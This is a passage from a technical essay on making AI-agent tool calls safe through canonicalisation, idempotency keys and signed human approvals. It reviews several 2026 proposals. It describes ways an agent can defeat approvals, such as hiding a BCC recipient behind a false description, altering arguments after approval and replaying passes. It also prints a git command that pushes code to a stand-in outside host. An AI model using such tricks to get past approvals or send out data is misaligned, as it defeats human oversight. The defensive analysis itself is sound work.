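| Hash the received bytes | Treats them as three payments | 3,751.50 euros |
| Parse, normalise and canonicalise | Recognises one payment and two copies | 1,250.50 euros |
| Accept only canonical bytes | Refuses all three | Nothing until the agent sends the canonical line |

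The third approach prevents the double payment, but it refuses even the first spelling, which most developers would consider normal. That line puts `tool` before `arguments`, lists the supplier before the amount, and gives the amount in euros instead of cents. To pass the guard, the model would have to sort the names, leave out every space, convert the amount to cents, and write the arguments before naming the tool they are for.

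Each mistake would lead to a refusal and usually a retry. In the Gecko experiment, allowing up to three retries more than doubled the average time and cost per task, although those retries corrected many kinds of mistakes. Retrying to fix the field order wouldn't make the payment safer, because the guard could have sorted the fields itself almost instantly. Having the model convert the amount to cents might even make the payment less safe, because a model that is off by a factor of ten still writes a valid canonical request, but for the wrong amount.

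A provider could constrain the model's output so that it always had the right order and spacing. But gateways often parse a call and write it out again, and if this added a single space, the guard would refuse the call over a change that neither the model nor an attacker had made. DER and CBOR are even less suitable for a model to write directly, since it would have to calculate lengths and produce binary codes. In practice the host would encode the call, so a program would already be canonicalising it.

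The rule is still useful for single fields that a model can easily get right. The grammar for decimal strings applies it to amounts, accepting `1250.50` and refusing `1250.5`. A model needs only one short instruction to comply, and the guard needs no code to reconcile different spellings.

For whole requests, the rule works best between the guard and the executor. Both are programs, and the guard can produce canonical bytes every time with almost no overhead. If the executor receives anything else, either the guard is faulty or someone has changed the message, so the executor should refuse to run it.

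## Giving equivalent actions one identity: Faramesh and CAVA

The canonical forms described so far make different spellings of the same tool call identical. But an agent can often do the same thing through several tools. It might install a program with a `deploy` tool, a `release` tool or a shell command, and RFC 8785 gives each of these calls different bytes, so a rule or an approval for one doesn't apply to the others. Two proposals from 2026, Faramesh and CAVA, are meant to give actions with the same effect one identity.

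### Faramesh's canonical action

*Faramesh* (Fatmi, 2026) describes a guard that translates every tool call into a Canonical Action Representation with seven fields: the actor on whose behalf the action happens, the target system, the operation, the resource, the parameters, the "blast radius" (how much the action can affect) and the context. The guard discards everything else, including the model's explanation for the action.

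Fatmi's example has two calls that deploy a payments service:

```
{"tool":"deploy","service":"payments","env":"prod"}
{"action":"release","target":"payments","environment":"production"}
```

The calls have no field name in common, and `payments` is the only value they share. Faramesh turns both into this action:

```
Operation:    deploy
Resource:     payments
Parameters:   environment = production
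Blast radius: environment
```

The guard needs a table of aliases to do this, because sorting and reformatting are not enough. The table records that `release` means `deploy`, that `prod` means `production`, and that the second tool puts the service in a field called `target`. Fatmi also counts the sentence "Deploy the payments service to production." as a version of the same action. The guard would have to interpret English to recognise it, but he describes this step only as parsing that extracts the relevant attributes. If a language model did the parsing, an attacker might be able to influence its output and therefore the action's identity.

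A wrong entry in the table gives different actions the same identity. Suppose `deploy` installs the newest build of the payments service, while `release` installs the last version that testers accepted. The canonical action does not include a version, so an approval to install the tested version would also cover the newest one. The owner of two tools has to compare everything they do, including their defaults, before declaring them equivalent.

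A missing entry has the opposite effect. Suppose the policy requires a person's approval for `production`, and the agent writes `prd`. If the guard passes unknown names through unchanged, the rule doesn't apply, and an executor that resolves `prd` to `production` deploys without approval. Fatmi requires a controlled vocabulary for operations. A guard needs one for every field its policy refers to, and it should refuse any value outside that vocabulary.

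### The digest and the developer's tests

The guard hashes the canonical action and permits, denies or defers it, for instance until a person approves. It records the decision with the action's digest, the policy version and a digest of the relevant system state. If it permits the action, it signs a permit that contains the action's digest. The executor refuses any action without a valid permit for its digest.

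Fatmi, who works for the company that develops Faramesh, tested a prototype on one Apple M1 computer. Canonicalisation took a median of 0.42 milliseconds and the whole decision took 2.24 milliseconds. Both are negligible compared with the time a language model takes to write a call. In one test, 10,000 repetitions of an action all gave the same hash. In another, 64 workers submitted the same action 1,000,000 times, and the executor never carried it out twice.

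The first test covers only one of the two conditions for a canonical form, since a function that gave every action the same hash would also pass it. The executor rejected all 10,000 attempts to use an old permit for a new action, so those actions had different digests from the originals, which is some evidence for the other condition. But Fatmi's program generated the test requests from a fixed list of changes, such as reordered parameters, `prod` in place of `production`, and defaults written out. A developer who knows the list can put every alias into the table. The results therefore show that the prototype applies its rules consistently and quickly, but not how often the rules would cover what real agents write.

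The duplicates test also used one guard process with one local record of decisions. A company running guards on several machines would need them to share that record, which is slower and can fail in more ways.

### A trailing space and a null field

Fatmi illustrates the system with a call that sends an email. One version of the call has a space at the end of the body and an extra field:

```
{"tool":"email.send","to":"a@x.com","subj":"hi","body":"ok ","meta":{"x":null}}
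```

Faramesh gives it the same canonical text, and so the same digest, as the plain version:

```
{"tool":"email.send","to":"a@x.com","subj":"hi","body":"ok"}
```

In an email, neither change is likely to matter. In other tools, both could. On Linux, a file name with a space at the end names a different file from the same name without it. In JSON Merge Patch, a standard format for updating records, null tells the server to delete a field. The example does not reveal whether Faramesh removed `meta` because the tool doesn't declare it or because it contained only a null. If it removes nulls everywhere, these two requests to a customer database get the same digest:

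```
{"customer":"C-31","changes":{}}
{"customer":"C-31","changes":{"phone":null}}
```

The first changes nothing, and the second deletes a phone number.

The danger depends on what the executor runs, and the paper is unclear about this. In its control model, the guard forwards the canonical action to execution, but a later section describes a guard that "does not proxy payloads". If the executor receives the agent's original call instead, it computes the canonical digest, finds that the digest matches the permit, and runs the original call, including everything the guard had removed. The phone number is then deleted under a valid permit, although nobody approved the deletion.

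Let c stand for canonicalisation, as before, and run for what the executor does. If the executor runs original calls, one permit is safe for two requests only if

c(r1) = c(r2) implies run(r1) = run(r2).

Somebody would have to establish this for every tool and every rule in the alias table. If the executor runs the canonical action instead, the corresponding condition is

c(r1) = c(r2) implies run(c(r1)) = run(c(r2)),

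which always holds when the system is in the same state, because both sides run the same thing. This is the same reason for which executing the parsed object worked in the study of repeated parsing. It also removes the problem with `deploy` and `release`, since a single program now carries out the canonical `deploy` action, whichever tool the agent named.

The agent might still get something other than what it asked for. Fatmi does not guarantee that the canonical action reflects the agent's intent or the real consequences of running it. A person who approves an action should therefore see the canonical version, and the host should tell the model what the guard changed.

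The email example is probably simplified, but a developer who copied it exactly would introduce two smaller faults. The canonical text leaves out the actor, so a permit for one agent would also match another agent's identical email. The fields are also not in alphabetical order, so an auditor using an RFC 8785 library would compute a different digest.

### CAVA and the case against approving text

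Wang (2026), in *CAVA*, whose company sells a product based on the system, starts from shell commands. These three all upload a branch of code called `main` to a server:

```
git push origin main
git -c push.default=simple push origin main
bash -c "git push origin main"
```

A policy that checks the first two words catches only the first command. A policy that searches for `git push` anywhere catches the third but also blocks a harmless documentation search for those words. Wang concludes that binding a decision to raw text is not enough, because different text with the same effect can evade it.

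How much this matters depends on what the guard does with text that no rule matches. If it forbids a list of commands and allows everything else, a rewritten command gets past it. If it allows only commands that someone has approved, it refuses the rewritten command, which then needs a second approval or a retry. Wang's argument is therefore stronger against lists of forbidden commands than against approvals.

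Approving text is also unreliable because the same text can have different effects. For example, `git push origin main` uploads whatever the `main` branch contains at that moment to whatever server the local settings call `origin`, so an approval given on Monday could cover different code on Tuesday. To prevent this, the canonical action would have to include the exact version of the code and the server's address.

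CAVA processes an action in seven stages:

1. Capture the event and the software it came from.
2. Normalise it into a canonical action.
3. Look for risk patterns, such as moving data to a public link.
4. Hash the canonical action to get a fingerprint.
5. Attach the policy decision or approval to the fingerprint.
6. Record the outcome.
7. Optionally, sign the record or have an outside party attest to it.

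The canonical action includes the program, the operation, a risk category, the systems it touches, its target and whether it is reversible, but none of the standard fields is an amount. In Wang's examples, a payment is the operation `payment_trigger` in the category `payment`, with an account as a possible target. If the fingerprint covers only the standard fields, payments of 1,250.50 and 12,505 euros to the same supplier have the same fingerprint. The definition allows extra metadata, and Wang lists the amount among the evidence for payments "when available", but the fingerprint covers only "selected" fields. An operator should check that these include the amount and currency.

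A fingerprint can also cover too many fields. CAVA's action records the runtime, which is the kind of software the agent acted through. If the fingerprint covered this field, the same upload would have different identities through a shell and through a tool server, which CAVA is meant to prevent.

Wang tested CAVA on 96 scenarios, expanded into 384 variants across shells, tool servers, browsers and hosted agents. CAVA scored 1.000 on all nine measures. A policy based on raw text scored zero on seven of them, and one based on a command's first words scored zero on six.

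These scores rest on fewer checks than the totals suggest. Wang tested equivalence on 12 rewritten actions, and tested whether CAVA kept different actions apart on 8 pairs. A system that failed on one rewriting in five would still pass all 12 about 7% of the time (0.8^12 ≈ 0.07) if they were chosen at random. Wang's were not, because he wrote both the cases and the system. The comparison with raw text is also lopsided, because that baseline scored zero for reproducible receipts even though anyone can recompute the hash of a text. It probably scored zero only because it issued no receipts.

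Wang describes the figures as regression evidence for this set of cases and asks outsiders to contribute attacks. The public version leaves out the parsers the company sells, so outsiders can't use it to test the full product. The cases are still useful to anyone building a guard because they list many ways to hide one command inside another.

### Telling a second payment from a retry

Faramesh's executor carries out a permitted action only if its digest has not been used before. This stops duplicates, but it can also stop payments that a company wants to make. An invoice number can distinguish two genuine payments of the same amount, but if the company pays supplier S-204 a fixed monthly fee of 1,250.50 euros without an invoice, each month's request has the same canonical form as the running example.

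The October payment uses up the digest. In November the agent sends the same request, and the executor refuses it as a duplicate. Fatmi lets a policy mark an action as repeatable, but then a retry after a timeout pays the October fee a second time.

An idempotency key can take the place of the invoice number. It is a value that identifies one intended action and stays the same however often a program attempts it. (An operation is idempotent if doing it twice has the same result as doing it once.) The guard keeps a record of each key with the digest of the request and the result, and follows three rules:

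- If the key is new, record it as pending and make the payment.
- If the key exists with the same digest, do not pay again. Return the stored result, or wait for it if the payment is pending.
- If the key exists with a different digest, refuse the request.

In the table, D1 is the digest of the monthly request's canonical form, without the key, and D2 is the digest of a request with a different amount.

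| Request | Key | Digest | What the guard does |
|---|---|---|---|
| October fee | `fee-2026-10` | D1 | Pays 1,250.50 euros |
| October retry, spelled differently | `fee-2026-10` | D1 | Returns the first result |
| November fee | `fee-2026-11` | D1 | Pays 1,250.50 euros |
| October key with 1,520.50 euros | `fee-2026-10` | D2 | Refuses |

The company pays the correct total of 2,501 euros. The key separates October from November, and the canonical form lets the guard accept the retry. If the guard hashed the raw text instead, the new spelling would give a different digest, and under the third rule the guard would refuse a legitimate retry.

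Trusted code should create the key, because a model might write a new one for each attempt, and an attacker could ask it to. The host could generate a random key and reuse it for its own retries, but if the session crashed and a new one restarted the task, as happened to Lobstar Wilde, the new session would generate a different key and the guard would pay again. In the example, the key comes from the company's payment schedule, so any session that pays the October fee gets the same key. This also prevents an attacker from getting a second key for the October fee.

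An approval has to cover the key as well as the digest. Otherwise a person who approved D1 for October would also have approved it for November.

A crash can still cause a double payment. Suppose the guard records the key as pending, sends the payment and crashes before it can store the result. After it restarts, its records don't show whether the bank received the payment. If the bank also accepts idempotency keys, the guard can safely send the same request and key again. If not, it should leave the payment pending until a person or program has checked the bank's records. Faramesh also marks an action as pending before it decides, which handles simultaneous requests well. Fatmi's test with a million duplicates covered simultaneous requests, but not a crash halfway through a payment.

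The guard must also keep keys as long as a retry could arrive. If it deletes them after a day, a job that restarts after a weekend can make the same payment again.

### An action reference that leaves out the arguments

Etcheverry and Ives (2026), in *Action Reference*, another individual Internet-Draft, define their own version of the `action_ref` in Hopley's draft. It is also a digest of the agent, the type of action, its scope and the time. For the running example, the hashed text might be:

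```
{"action_type":"payment.send","agent_id":"payer-7","scope":"S-204","timestamp":"2026-10-07T09:00:00.000Z"}
```

Anyone who has the four values can compute the reference without asking the company that issued it. The timestamp must be text with exactly three decimal places, whereas Hopley requires a whole number of milliseconds. Two systems that follow different drafts therefore compute different references for the same action.

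Like Hopley's version, this one leaves out the call's arguments, so two different calls by the same agent share a reference if they have the same type, scope and millisecond. A model can ask for several tool calls in one message, and a host might stamp the whole batch with one time. Payments of 900 and 9,000 euros to S-204 would then have the same reference. Even if the host stamps each call separately, there is about a 4% chance that at least two of ten such calls, made at random moments within one second, fall in the same millisecond.

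The draft forbids developers from putting a hash of the whole request into the scope field to tell the calls apart, because a verifier would then need another record to work out the scope.

A retry has the opposite problem. It normally has a new timestamp and therefore a new reference, so a duplicate check based on `action_ref` would let the second payment through. The host could avoid this by keeping the first attempt's timestamp. The reference would then work somewhat like an idempotency key, though two different payments might still share it.

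Etcheverry and Ives designed `action_ref` mainly to connect the records that several systems keep about one action. For this, they add separate digests of the arguments that the agent proposed and those that the system finally sent. A verifier compares both digests, along with `action_ref` and an authorisation identifier. That identifier is a hash of `action_ref`, the authorised scope, the time of the decision and the policy, so it doesn't cover the arguments either. A verifier that skipped the argument digests could accept a receipt for 9,000 euros under an approval for 900. Etcheverry and Ives also warn that `action_ref` alone cannot detect a replay.

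### Shell commands, file paths and URLs

The owner of a payment tool can define what its few fields mean, but a shell command is a small program, and no algorithm can decide for every pair of programs whether they have the same effect. Suppose a script runs P, a program that only calculates, and then deletes a file. The script has the same effect as doing nothing exactly when P never finishes. An algorithm that compared effects could therefore determine whether any given program finishes, which Alan Turing proved impossible in 1936.

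A guard can still compare simple commands, as long as it recognises the ones it doesn't understand. Wang's second `git` command shows how easily this goes wrong. Its `-c` option changes a setting for one run, and in that command the setting makes no difference. Here the same option sends the code to another server:

```
git -c remote.origin.pushurl=https://other.example/x push origin main
```

If the guard removes every `-c` option to get a canonical command, an approval of the ordinary upload also covers this one. The guard therefore has to account for what each setting does and reject any it doesn't recognise.

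File paths and URLs look simpler, but whether two of them are equivalent often depends on facts outside the text.

| First form | Second form | When they are equivalent |
|---|---|---|
| `/srv/reports/../a.pdf` | `/srv/a.pdf` | If `reports` is not a link to a folder elsewhere |
| `Report.txt` | `report.txt` | If the file system ignores case |
| `https://example.com:443/a` | `https://example.com/a` | Always, because 443 is the default port |
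| `https://example.com/a?x=1&y=2` | `https://example.com/a?y=2&x=1` | If the server ignores the order |
| `http://2130706433/` | `http://127.0.0.1/` | If the client accepts an address written as one number |

In the first row, suppose `/srv/reports` is a symbolic link to `/archive/2025`. Linux then resolves `..` to `/archive`, so the path refers to `/archive/a.pdf`. A guard that simplified the path as text would check the permissions of `/srv/a.pdf`, while the executor would open `/archive/a.pdf`.

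Equivalence can also depend on the operation. A file on Linux can have two names, called hard links. Writing to the file under either name changes the same contents, but deleting one name leaves the file available under the other. The names are therefore equivalent for writing but not for deleting.

The target of a path or URL can also change after the guard checks it. Someone can point a symbolic link at another folder, and a website can redirect an approved URL to a different address. For paths, trusted code can open the file once, check what it opened, and pass the open file to the executor instead of the path. For URLs, it can check every redirect and the network address of each connection before sending anything.

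### When the guard cannot normalise a request

A guard needs a defined response to a request that it cannot translate. In *Who Holds the Pen?*, Li, Ma and colleagues (2026) build one into SpecHarness, which turns an agent's instructions and tool documentation into requirements and checks the agent's actions and results against them. SpecHarness compares each proposed action with its canonical actions and labels the result exact, normalised or unmatched. It then checks exact and normalised actions against the requirements and returns "allow", "block" or "unclear". Where a requirement can block an action that SpecHarness fully controls, the action runs only if the check returns "allow".

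An unmatched action has four possible outcomes. SpecHarness raises an error if it should have recognised the action, and rejects the action if it has no support for it. If the operator has declared the action out of scope, the system's ordinary policy applies. The fourth possibility is to run the action in an isolated environment and check the result before accepting it. This is reasonable for a program that writes a file in a temporary folder, but useless for a bank transfer, because checking the result does not reverse the transfer.

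Refusing unmatched actions helps only if the agent has no other way to achieve the same effect. Li and colleagues call an action closed if every available path to its effect either goes through the check or is blocked. For the payment tool, this would mean the agent has no browser logged in to the bank and no shell with the bank's credentials. The operator then doesn't have to recognise every command that could make a payment, because none of them would work. In the tests on SkillsBench, a set of 87 practical tasks, 44% of the binding requirements concerned closed actions. SpecHarness checked the rest after execution.

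Across seven models, SpecHarness raised the average share of tasks that passed the official tests from 61.1% to 73.1%. The share of runs that the system accepted as complete but that failed those tests fell from 32.8% to 12.8%. With GPT-5.6 Sol, the pass rate was 85.1% for the full system and 80.5% without the stage that checks actions before they run. That stage includes normalisation and authorisation, so the difference does not measure normalisation alone. The tasks also measure how well agents do ordinary work, not whether an attacker could disguise a forbidden action.

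Wang faces the same problem with private scripts, because it is hard to tell what they do from their names. He recommends marking CAVA's coverage of them as lower and requiring a dedicated parser, a sandbox trial run or human review.

For tools that move money, change permissions or delete data, a guard should refuse an unmatched request and return an error that names a structured tool for the same job. The model can then try again with `pay_supplier` instead of a shell command. A coding agent often needs a shell, though, and a person may have to approve commands that no parser understands. The approval should cover the exact text, the folder in which the command runs and the contents of any script it calls, and the command should run without credentials it doesn't need. The guard should never treat such a command as equivalent to one that someone has already approved, because a wrong guess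 would run a command that nobody approved, which is worse than asking a person to approve the same thing twice.

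## Approvals signed over one exact action

When a policy requires a person's approval, the guard holds the request and asks for it. The approval is useful only if the agent cannot produce it and it covers exactly the request the executor carries out. Agent frameworks often fail the second condition. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) examined how ten of them handle approval. Four of the eight approval mechanisms whose behaviour could be measured let someone change the request after approval and then ran the new version. LangGraph and Agno, for example, run whatever arguments are in the saved session when it resumes. A program that controls the session could get approval for a payment of 900 euros and have the framework pay 9,000.

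European rules for online payments already require the code that confirms a payment to be linked to the amount and the payee, and changing either one invalidates the code. Kodathala and colleagues extend this rule to every argument of a tool call.

### One approval, message by message

Their design, Agent Step-Up (ASU), puts a gateway on a separate computer between the agent and its tools. The gateway is both guard and executor. The user's phone holds a passkey, a private key that it uses only after the user unlocks it, for instance with a fingerprint. An approval goes through these steps:

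1. The agent sends the gateway a tool call and may add an explanation in plain language.
2. The gateway checks the call against a closed schema, normalises the arguments and builds a descriptor of the effect. It serialises the descriptor under RFC 8785 and computes its SHA-256 digest, h.
3. If the policy requires approval, the gateway stores the descriptor and gives the agent only an identifier for the pending request.
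4. The user opens the gateway's approval page on the phone. The page shows a card that the gateway has drawn from the descriptor.
5. If the user approves, the phone signs a challenge that depends on h.
6. The gateway verifies the signature and keeps it as a receipt.
7. The agent sends the identifier again. The gateway marks the approval as used and runs the stored descriptor. If the agent also sends arguments and they give a different digest, the gateway returns an error and runs nothing.

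The challenge is itself a digest of a small canonical object:

```
c = SHA-256(JCS({tag: "ASU-APPROVAL-v2", digest: h, approval_id: id,
                 nonce: n, grant_digest: g}))
```

JCS is the serialisation from RFC 8785, and n is a random value for this approval. The last field is null unless the user ticks "allow similar", which creates a limited permission for later calls. Because the fields are in a JSON object, text cannot move from one field to another, as it could in Amazon's early signatures.

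Kodathala and colleagues list seven properties that an approval should have:

| Property | What it requires | How ASU provides it |
|---|---|---|
| Agent independence | Nothing the agent controls can produce an approval | The key is on the phone, and the agent sees only an identifier |
| Effect binding | The action that runs has the digest the user signed | The gateway runs the stored descriptor |
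| Single use | One approval causes at most one execution, before it expires | The gateway marks it as used in one indivisible step |
| Trusted rendering | The card comes from the descriptor, and different descriptors give different cards | The gateway draws the card |
| Non-repudiation | An outsider can verify which digest the user's key signed | The receipt needs only the public key |
| Scope integrity | "Allow similar" covers only what the user agreed to | Recipients, accounts, paths and URLs stay fixed |
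| Flood resistance | The agent cannot win approval by asking repeatedly | The gateway limits requests and locks out an agent after three refusals |

The gateway's rule for normalising URLs looks risky because it keeps only the scheme, host, port and path, and drops the query after the question mark. If the gateway then ran the reduced URL, the card would match the action, but a request to export one customer's record could become a request to export every customer's. A safer rule would keep the query or refuse URLs that have one.

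### Why the card must come from the signed object

A passkey signs the challenge but does not display it, so the user knows only what the page shows. In one of the tests, a user asks an agent to email a report to their boss. The agent adds a hidden copy to an outside address and describes the email without mentioning the copy. Kodathala and colleagues gave this description to 15 language models acting as approvers, and all 15 approved. They then showed the models ASU's card, which listed both addresses, and all 15 refused.

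If the agent writes the card, a valid signature can cover an action the user didn't mean to approve. The user believes they are approving an email to one person, but the phone signs the digest of the email with the hidden copy. In a formal model of this design, built in the protocol checker Tamarin, the user's key had likewise signed the action that ran, though the user had not approved it.

The descriptor and its digest leave out the agent's explanation. If they included it, the same payment would have a different digest whenever the explanation changed. A false explanation would also make the signature ambiguous, because the signature would cover both a payment of 500 euros to a stranger and a sentence describing a payment of 5 euros to a friend. ASU shows the explanation in a collapsed box labelled as untrusted.

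The card also has to look different for each different action. The Model Context Protocol lets a server ask the user a question, and its Python library forwards the server's text unchanged. In one test, payments of 10 and 10,000 to different accounts produced identical questions, and both ran after the user accepted. ASU's card puts text values in quotation marks, so the text "true" looks different from the value true. It lists every recipient in the title and replaces long runs of invisible characters with a visible count. It also puts field names chosen by the agent in a separate section, so a field called `Verified by client` can't be mistaken for the gateway's own label.

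The user still has to trust the gateway's page, because a malicious page could show one card and have the phone sign the challenge for another. Kodathala and colleagues mention an earlier paper in which Weng pursues the same goal for coding agents but assumes a trustworthy path to the user instead of building one. ASU builds most of that path but still depends on the page and the phone being trustworthy.

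### How well ASU worked

The evaluation used 27,108 scripted trials and 609 attack cases from AgentDojo, a public benchmark for prompt injection. Simulated people did the approving.

| Attack | Success against a weaker design | Success against ASU |
|---|---|---|
| Arguments changed after approval | 100%, if the approval does not name the action | 0% |
| Used approval presented again | 100%, if the approval does not name the action | 0% |
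| False description, approver compares the card with the task | 54%, if the agent writes the card | 3% |
| False description, approver believes the agent | 54%, if the agent writes the card | 54%, or 5% with the explanation removed |
| Repeated requests until one succeeds | 100%, without limits on requests | 45% to 60% |

The first two rows are the most reliable because the design explains their results. A gateway that runs only the stored action ignores any later substitute, however careless the approver is. Tamarin also proved effect binding and single use for any number of sessions. Effect binding depends on three assumptions: the user decides based on the card, only the user can register their first passkey, and the page behaves as designed. Tamarin found an attack when any one of these assumptions was removed.

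The other rows depend on how the researchers simulated people. The 3% comes from a simulated approver that compares the whole card with a correct one, which no real person could do. The figures for repeated requests assume that a user has a fixed chance of overlooking each kind of change. They support limits on requests, but they don't predict how often a real user would give in.

The results for language models apply more directly to practice, since some companies already use models as approvers. The 15 models refused 30% of the attacks when they saw the agent's description and 98% when they saw the card. They also refused 16% of harmless requests when they saw the card, but none when they saw the description. Most of these refusals cited placeholder text such as `<report placeholder>`, which the researchers had used instead of real email bodies. Without those refusals, the rate would have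 been about 2%.

The phone added no measurable protection. A trusted card on the agent's own computer did as well in 137 of 140 comparisons, and the other three differences were due to the "allow similar" option. This is to be expected, since no experiment gave the attacker control of that computer's display. A phone is worth the extra effort when the computer may be compromised, or when the company may have to prove the approval to an outsider.

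### ZeroGate's signed pass

Software can also issue approvals. Wang (2026), in *ZeroGate*, builds on his CAVA system and has an automated issuer sign a pass for one exact action, often before the agent is ready to carry it out. The issuer sorts the names in every object, keeps lists in order and writes the result as JSON. It refuses NaN and infinity. It then computes a SHA-256 digest of the pass, leaving out the field that will hold the digest, and makes an Ed25519 signature over two lines of text:

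```
osuite.zerogate.pass.v1
1cdbada39c5b2882d0de67e22c85ef6ad505512e2cd0727f36b089e03fc58d20
```

The fixed first line separates this use of the key from others, as DSSE's message type and ASU's tag do. The second line is the digest from one of Wang's test records.

Wang does not claim that his serialisation follows RFC 8785. His program runs on JavaScript, whose number format the RFC adopts, so the two probably agree on ordinary requests. Anyone writing a verifier in another language would need test vectors to confirm that its output matches. Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit also binds approvals to a digest, but it writes decimal numbers as Python does. Kodathala and colleagues found that three of five sample numbers would have different digests in a verifier that followed the RFC. Such a mismatch blocks a valid action but does not allow a wrong one.

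When the agent is ready to act, trusted code rebuilds the action from the data it is about to send, and a gate compares the result with the pass. The gate then marks the pass as used and writes a receipt in a single database transaction. In one test, eight processes presented the same pass at once, and the gate accepted only one. In another, Wang killed the program after the transaction but before it sent anything. The pass stayed marked as used, a second attempt failed, and he had to complete the request from a saved copy.

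Testing also exposed an expiry bug. The gate checked the time before waiting for database access, so a pass could expire during the wait and still count as valid. Wang changed the gate to check the time after the wait.

Early approval speeds up the final check but slows the upload overall. Over 1,600 file uploads, with 32 running at once, 95% of final checks took under 10 milliseconds when the approval was ready and under 334 milliseconds when it was not. The average upload, including preparation and waiting, took 2.0 seconds with early approval and 0.5 seconds without it. The longer wait also leaves more time for the facts behind the approval to change.

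### What the signature must cover

Checking an approval takes more than comparing the arguments. Wang tested a check that compared only the action with the pass, and it wrongly allowed 1,200 of 1,360 requests that his full set of checks refused. He wrote the cases himself, so the proportion applies only to his test, but they include many ways to misuse an approval without changing the action. Das (2026) lists similar failures in an individual Internet-Draft, *Tool Selection Is Not Execution*, and has the executor refuse each with its own error.

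| Signed item | Failure it prevents |
|---|---|
| Tool and schema version | The tool's owner changes a default or a unit, and an old approval takes on a new meaning |
| Principal, the person or department the agent acts for, and the agent | Another agent uses the approval, or the money comes from another department's budget |
| Recipient system | An approval for a test system works on the live one, or a malicious server offers a tool with the same name |
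| Policy version | The company tightens a rule, and an approval under the old rule still works |
| Nonce, a random value that the executor accepts once | One approval pays twice |
| Expiry | Someone uses a forgotten approval months later |
| Type of record | A signed log entry passes as an approval |

Suppose supplier S-204 has recently changed its bank account, and the policy requires a person to approve the first payment to a new account. The record for the payment of 1,250.50 euros could then look like this, with line breaks added for reading:

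```
{"agent":"payer-7",
 "arguments":{"amount_cents":125050,"currency":"EUR","invoice":"R-5512","supplier":"S-204"},
 "expires_at_ms":1791363900000,
 "issued_at_ms":1791363600000,
 "nonce":"(random value)",
 "payee_account":"(account number)",
 "policy_version":"2026-10-01",
 "principal":"accounts-payable",
 "recipient_system":"payments-live",
 "schema_digest":"(SHA-256 of the reviewed schema)",
 "tool":"pay_supplier",
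 "type":"payment-approval-v1"}
```

The two times are 9:00 and 9:05 UTC on 7 October 2026. The agent supplied only the arguments, and trusted code added the rest. The record needs the account number because the agent names a supplier but the bank pays an account. If the record contained only `S-204`, someone could change the supplier's details at 9:02 and redirect an approved payment without changing the request.

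The guard canonicalises the record, renders the approval card from it and puts the record's digest in the challenge that the phone signs. Before paying, the executor recomputes the digest and verifies the signature. It also checks that the record names this executor and the current schema and policy, and that it has not expired. It then claims the nonce and pays the amount in the record to the account in the record.

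The duplicate check still needs the invoice number, even though each approval has a nonce. If a person approves the same invoice twice by mistake, the two approvals have different nonces, so the executor can detect the duplicate only by the invoice number. The executor can delete a nonce soon after the approval expires, because the expiry check will reject any later use. It has to keep records of paid invoices much longer.

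If the guard checks the policy version strictly, any edit to the policy cancels every pending approval. This hardly matters for approvals that last five minutes. For longer ones, the guard could re-evaluate the request under the new policy and ask the person only if the decision has changed.

Das also requires a digest of the arguments, but his format lets a system label its canonical form "implementation-defined" instead of naming RFC 8785. An outside verifier could not recompute that digest without knowing the system's own rules, so a signed record should name a published scheme.

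### What each signature proves

An agent's signature shows which agent, or at least which key, sent a request. The signature is valid even if a malicious invoice caused the agent to send the request. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) describes a scheme in which an agent signs each action together with two flags. The first flag is set if the action is within the agent's standing permissions, and the second if a person approved this specific action. When the second flag is set, the record must also contain that person's passkey signature over the same data, so the agent can't set the flag on its own.

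A guard's signature shows that the guard reached a decision, but not that the policy was right or that the guard had current facts. In ZeroGate, it also doesn't show that the gate accepted the pass, because the file storage service checks a receipt supplied by the caller, and a program with the service's credential could invent one. The executor should therefore verify a signature from the gate or accept connections only from the gate.

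A person's signature is evidence of consent if the page showed them the action they signed. The executor also needs a trustworthy record of who owns the signing key. If a user has no passkey yet and anyone can register the first one, the agent can register its own and approve its own requests. ASU prevents this by requiring a one-time code sent to the user through a separate channel. When a language model approves a request, its signature counts as a guard's decision, and Microsoft's toolkit rightly rejects it where the policy requires a person.

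None of these signatures shows that the action is wise. A person may approve copying a customer list to a shared folder on Monday and making the folder public on Tuesday. Each card is accurate, but together the two actions publish the list. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) addresses this by tracking where data came from and showing the approver what the pending action would complete. Payments need a similar check on totals. In the ASU tests, when the policy didn't limit the total, an agent could always pay out a total of 500 dollars in payments of 50, because each payment was too small to need approval.

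### When the world changes after approval

Suppose the company blocks supplier S-204 at 9:03 on suspicion of fraud. The approval still has a valid signature, unchanged arguments and two minutes left, so it would pass those checks even though the supplier is now blocked. A shorter expiry makes this less likely but leaves people less time to read the card.

*Beyond Approved Actions* (Zhang, Zhang et al., 2026) describes EffectMatch, a system that ties each approval to a revision of the relevant state. Blocking the supplier creates a new revision, so the old approval no longer authorises the payment. Each approval also belongs to one execution, which must claim it before making any change. If the program crashes after claiming the approval, the approval stays used. *Agenra* (2026), a language for agent permissions, likewise counts an approval as used even if the tool fails. A person may then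 have to approve the same action again, but a crash can't allow one approval to be used to pay twice.

ZeroGate's state check compares each pass with a local copy of the policy and state versions, but nothing in the prototype keeps that copy up to date. If head office blocks the supplier and the copy doesn't change, the pass still matches the copy and the check misses the block. Two gates with separate databases would also each accept the same pass once. The executor should therefore read the supplier's status from the system that controls it, and all executors should claim nonces from one shared store.

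Even a correct check leaves a gap before the action takes effect. A database can close it by locking the relevant records from the check until the change is final, as EffectMatch does. Some services accept a condition as part of the request, as with ZeroGate's uploads, which succeed only if no file with that name exists. A bank transfer usually can't be made conditional on the company's own records, so it can still go through if the supplier is blocked between the check and the transfer. Das's draft has the executor use up the approval and call the tool in one indivisible step, but this is possible only when both happen in the same database.

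The action can also do more than the approval describes. In EffectMatch's main example, a person approves marking invoice 4711 as paid, and an automatic rule in the database also sends a notification. EffectMatch has the application list the permitted changes in advance. It runs the command in an unfinished transaction, records what changed, and commits only if

observed changes = approved changes.

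Here it finds the extra notification and undoes both changes. Zhang and colleagues introduced faults that led to 144 wrong results across three database tasks and twelve business tasks. EffectMatch rejected all of them and completed every normal run. When the researchers removed the link between an approval and one execution, the system accepted all 45 test runs that used another execution's approval, although the results were correct.

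These are strong results for databases, but the researchers chose which faults to test, and someone has to specify the permitted changes for every kind of task. The approvals also carry an HMAC instead of a public-key signature, so anyone who can verify an approval can also forge one. That may be acceptable within a company, but it means an approval proves little to an outsider.

A remote payment cannot be held in an unfinished transaction. If the bank's reply gets lost, EffectMatch records the result as unknown, stops the steps that depend on it and does not send the payment again. The old approval cannot authorise another attempt, even if the payment never happened.
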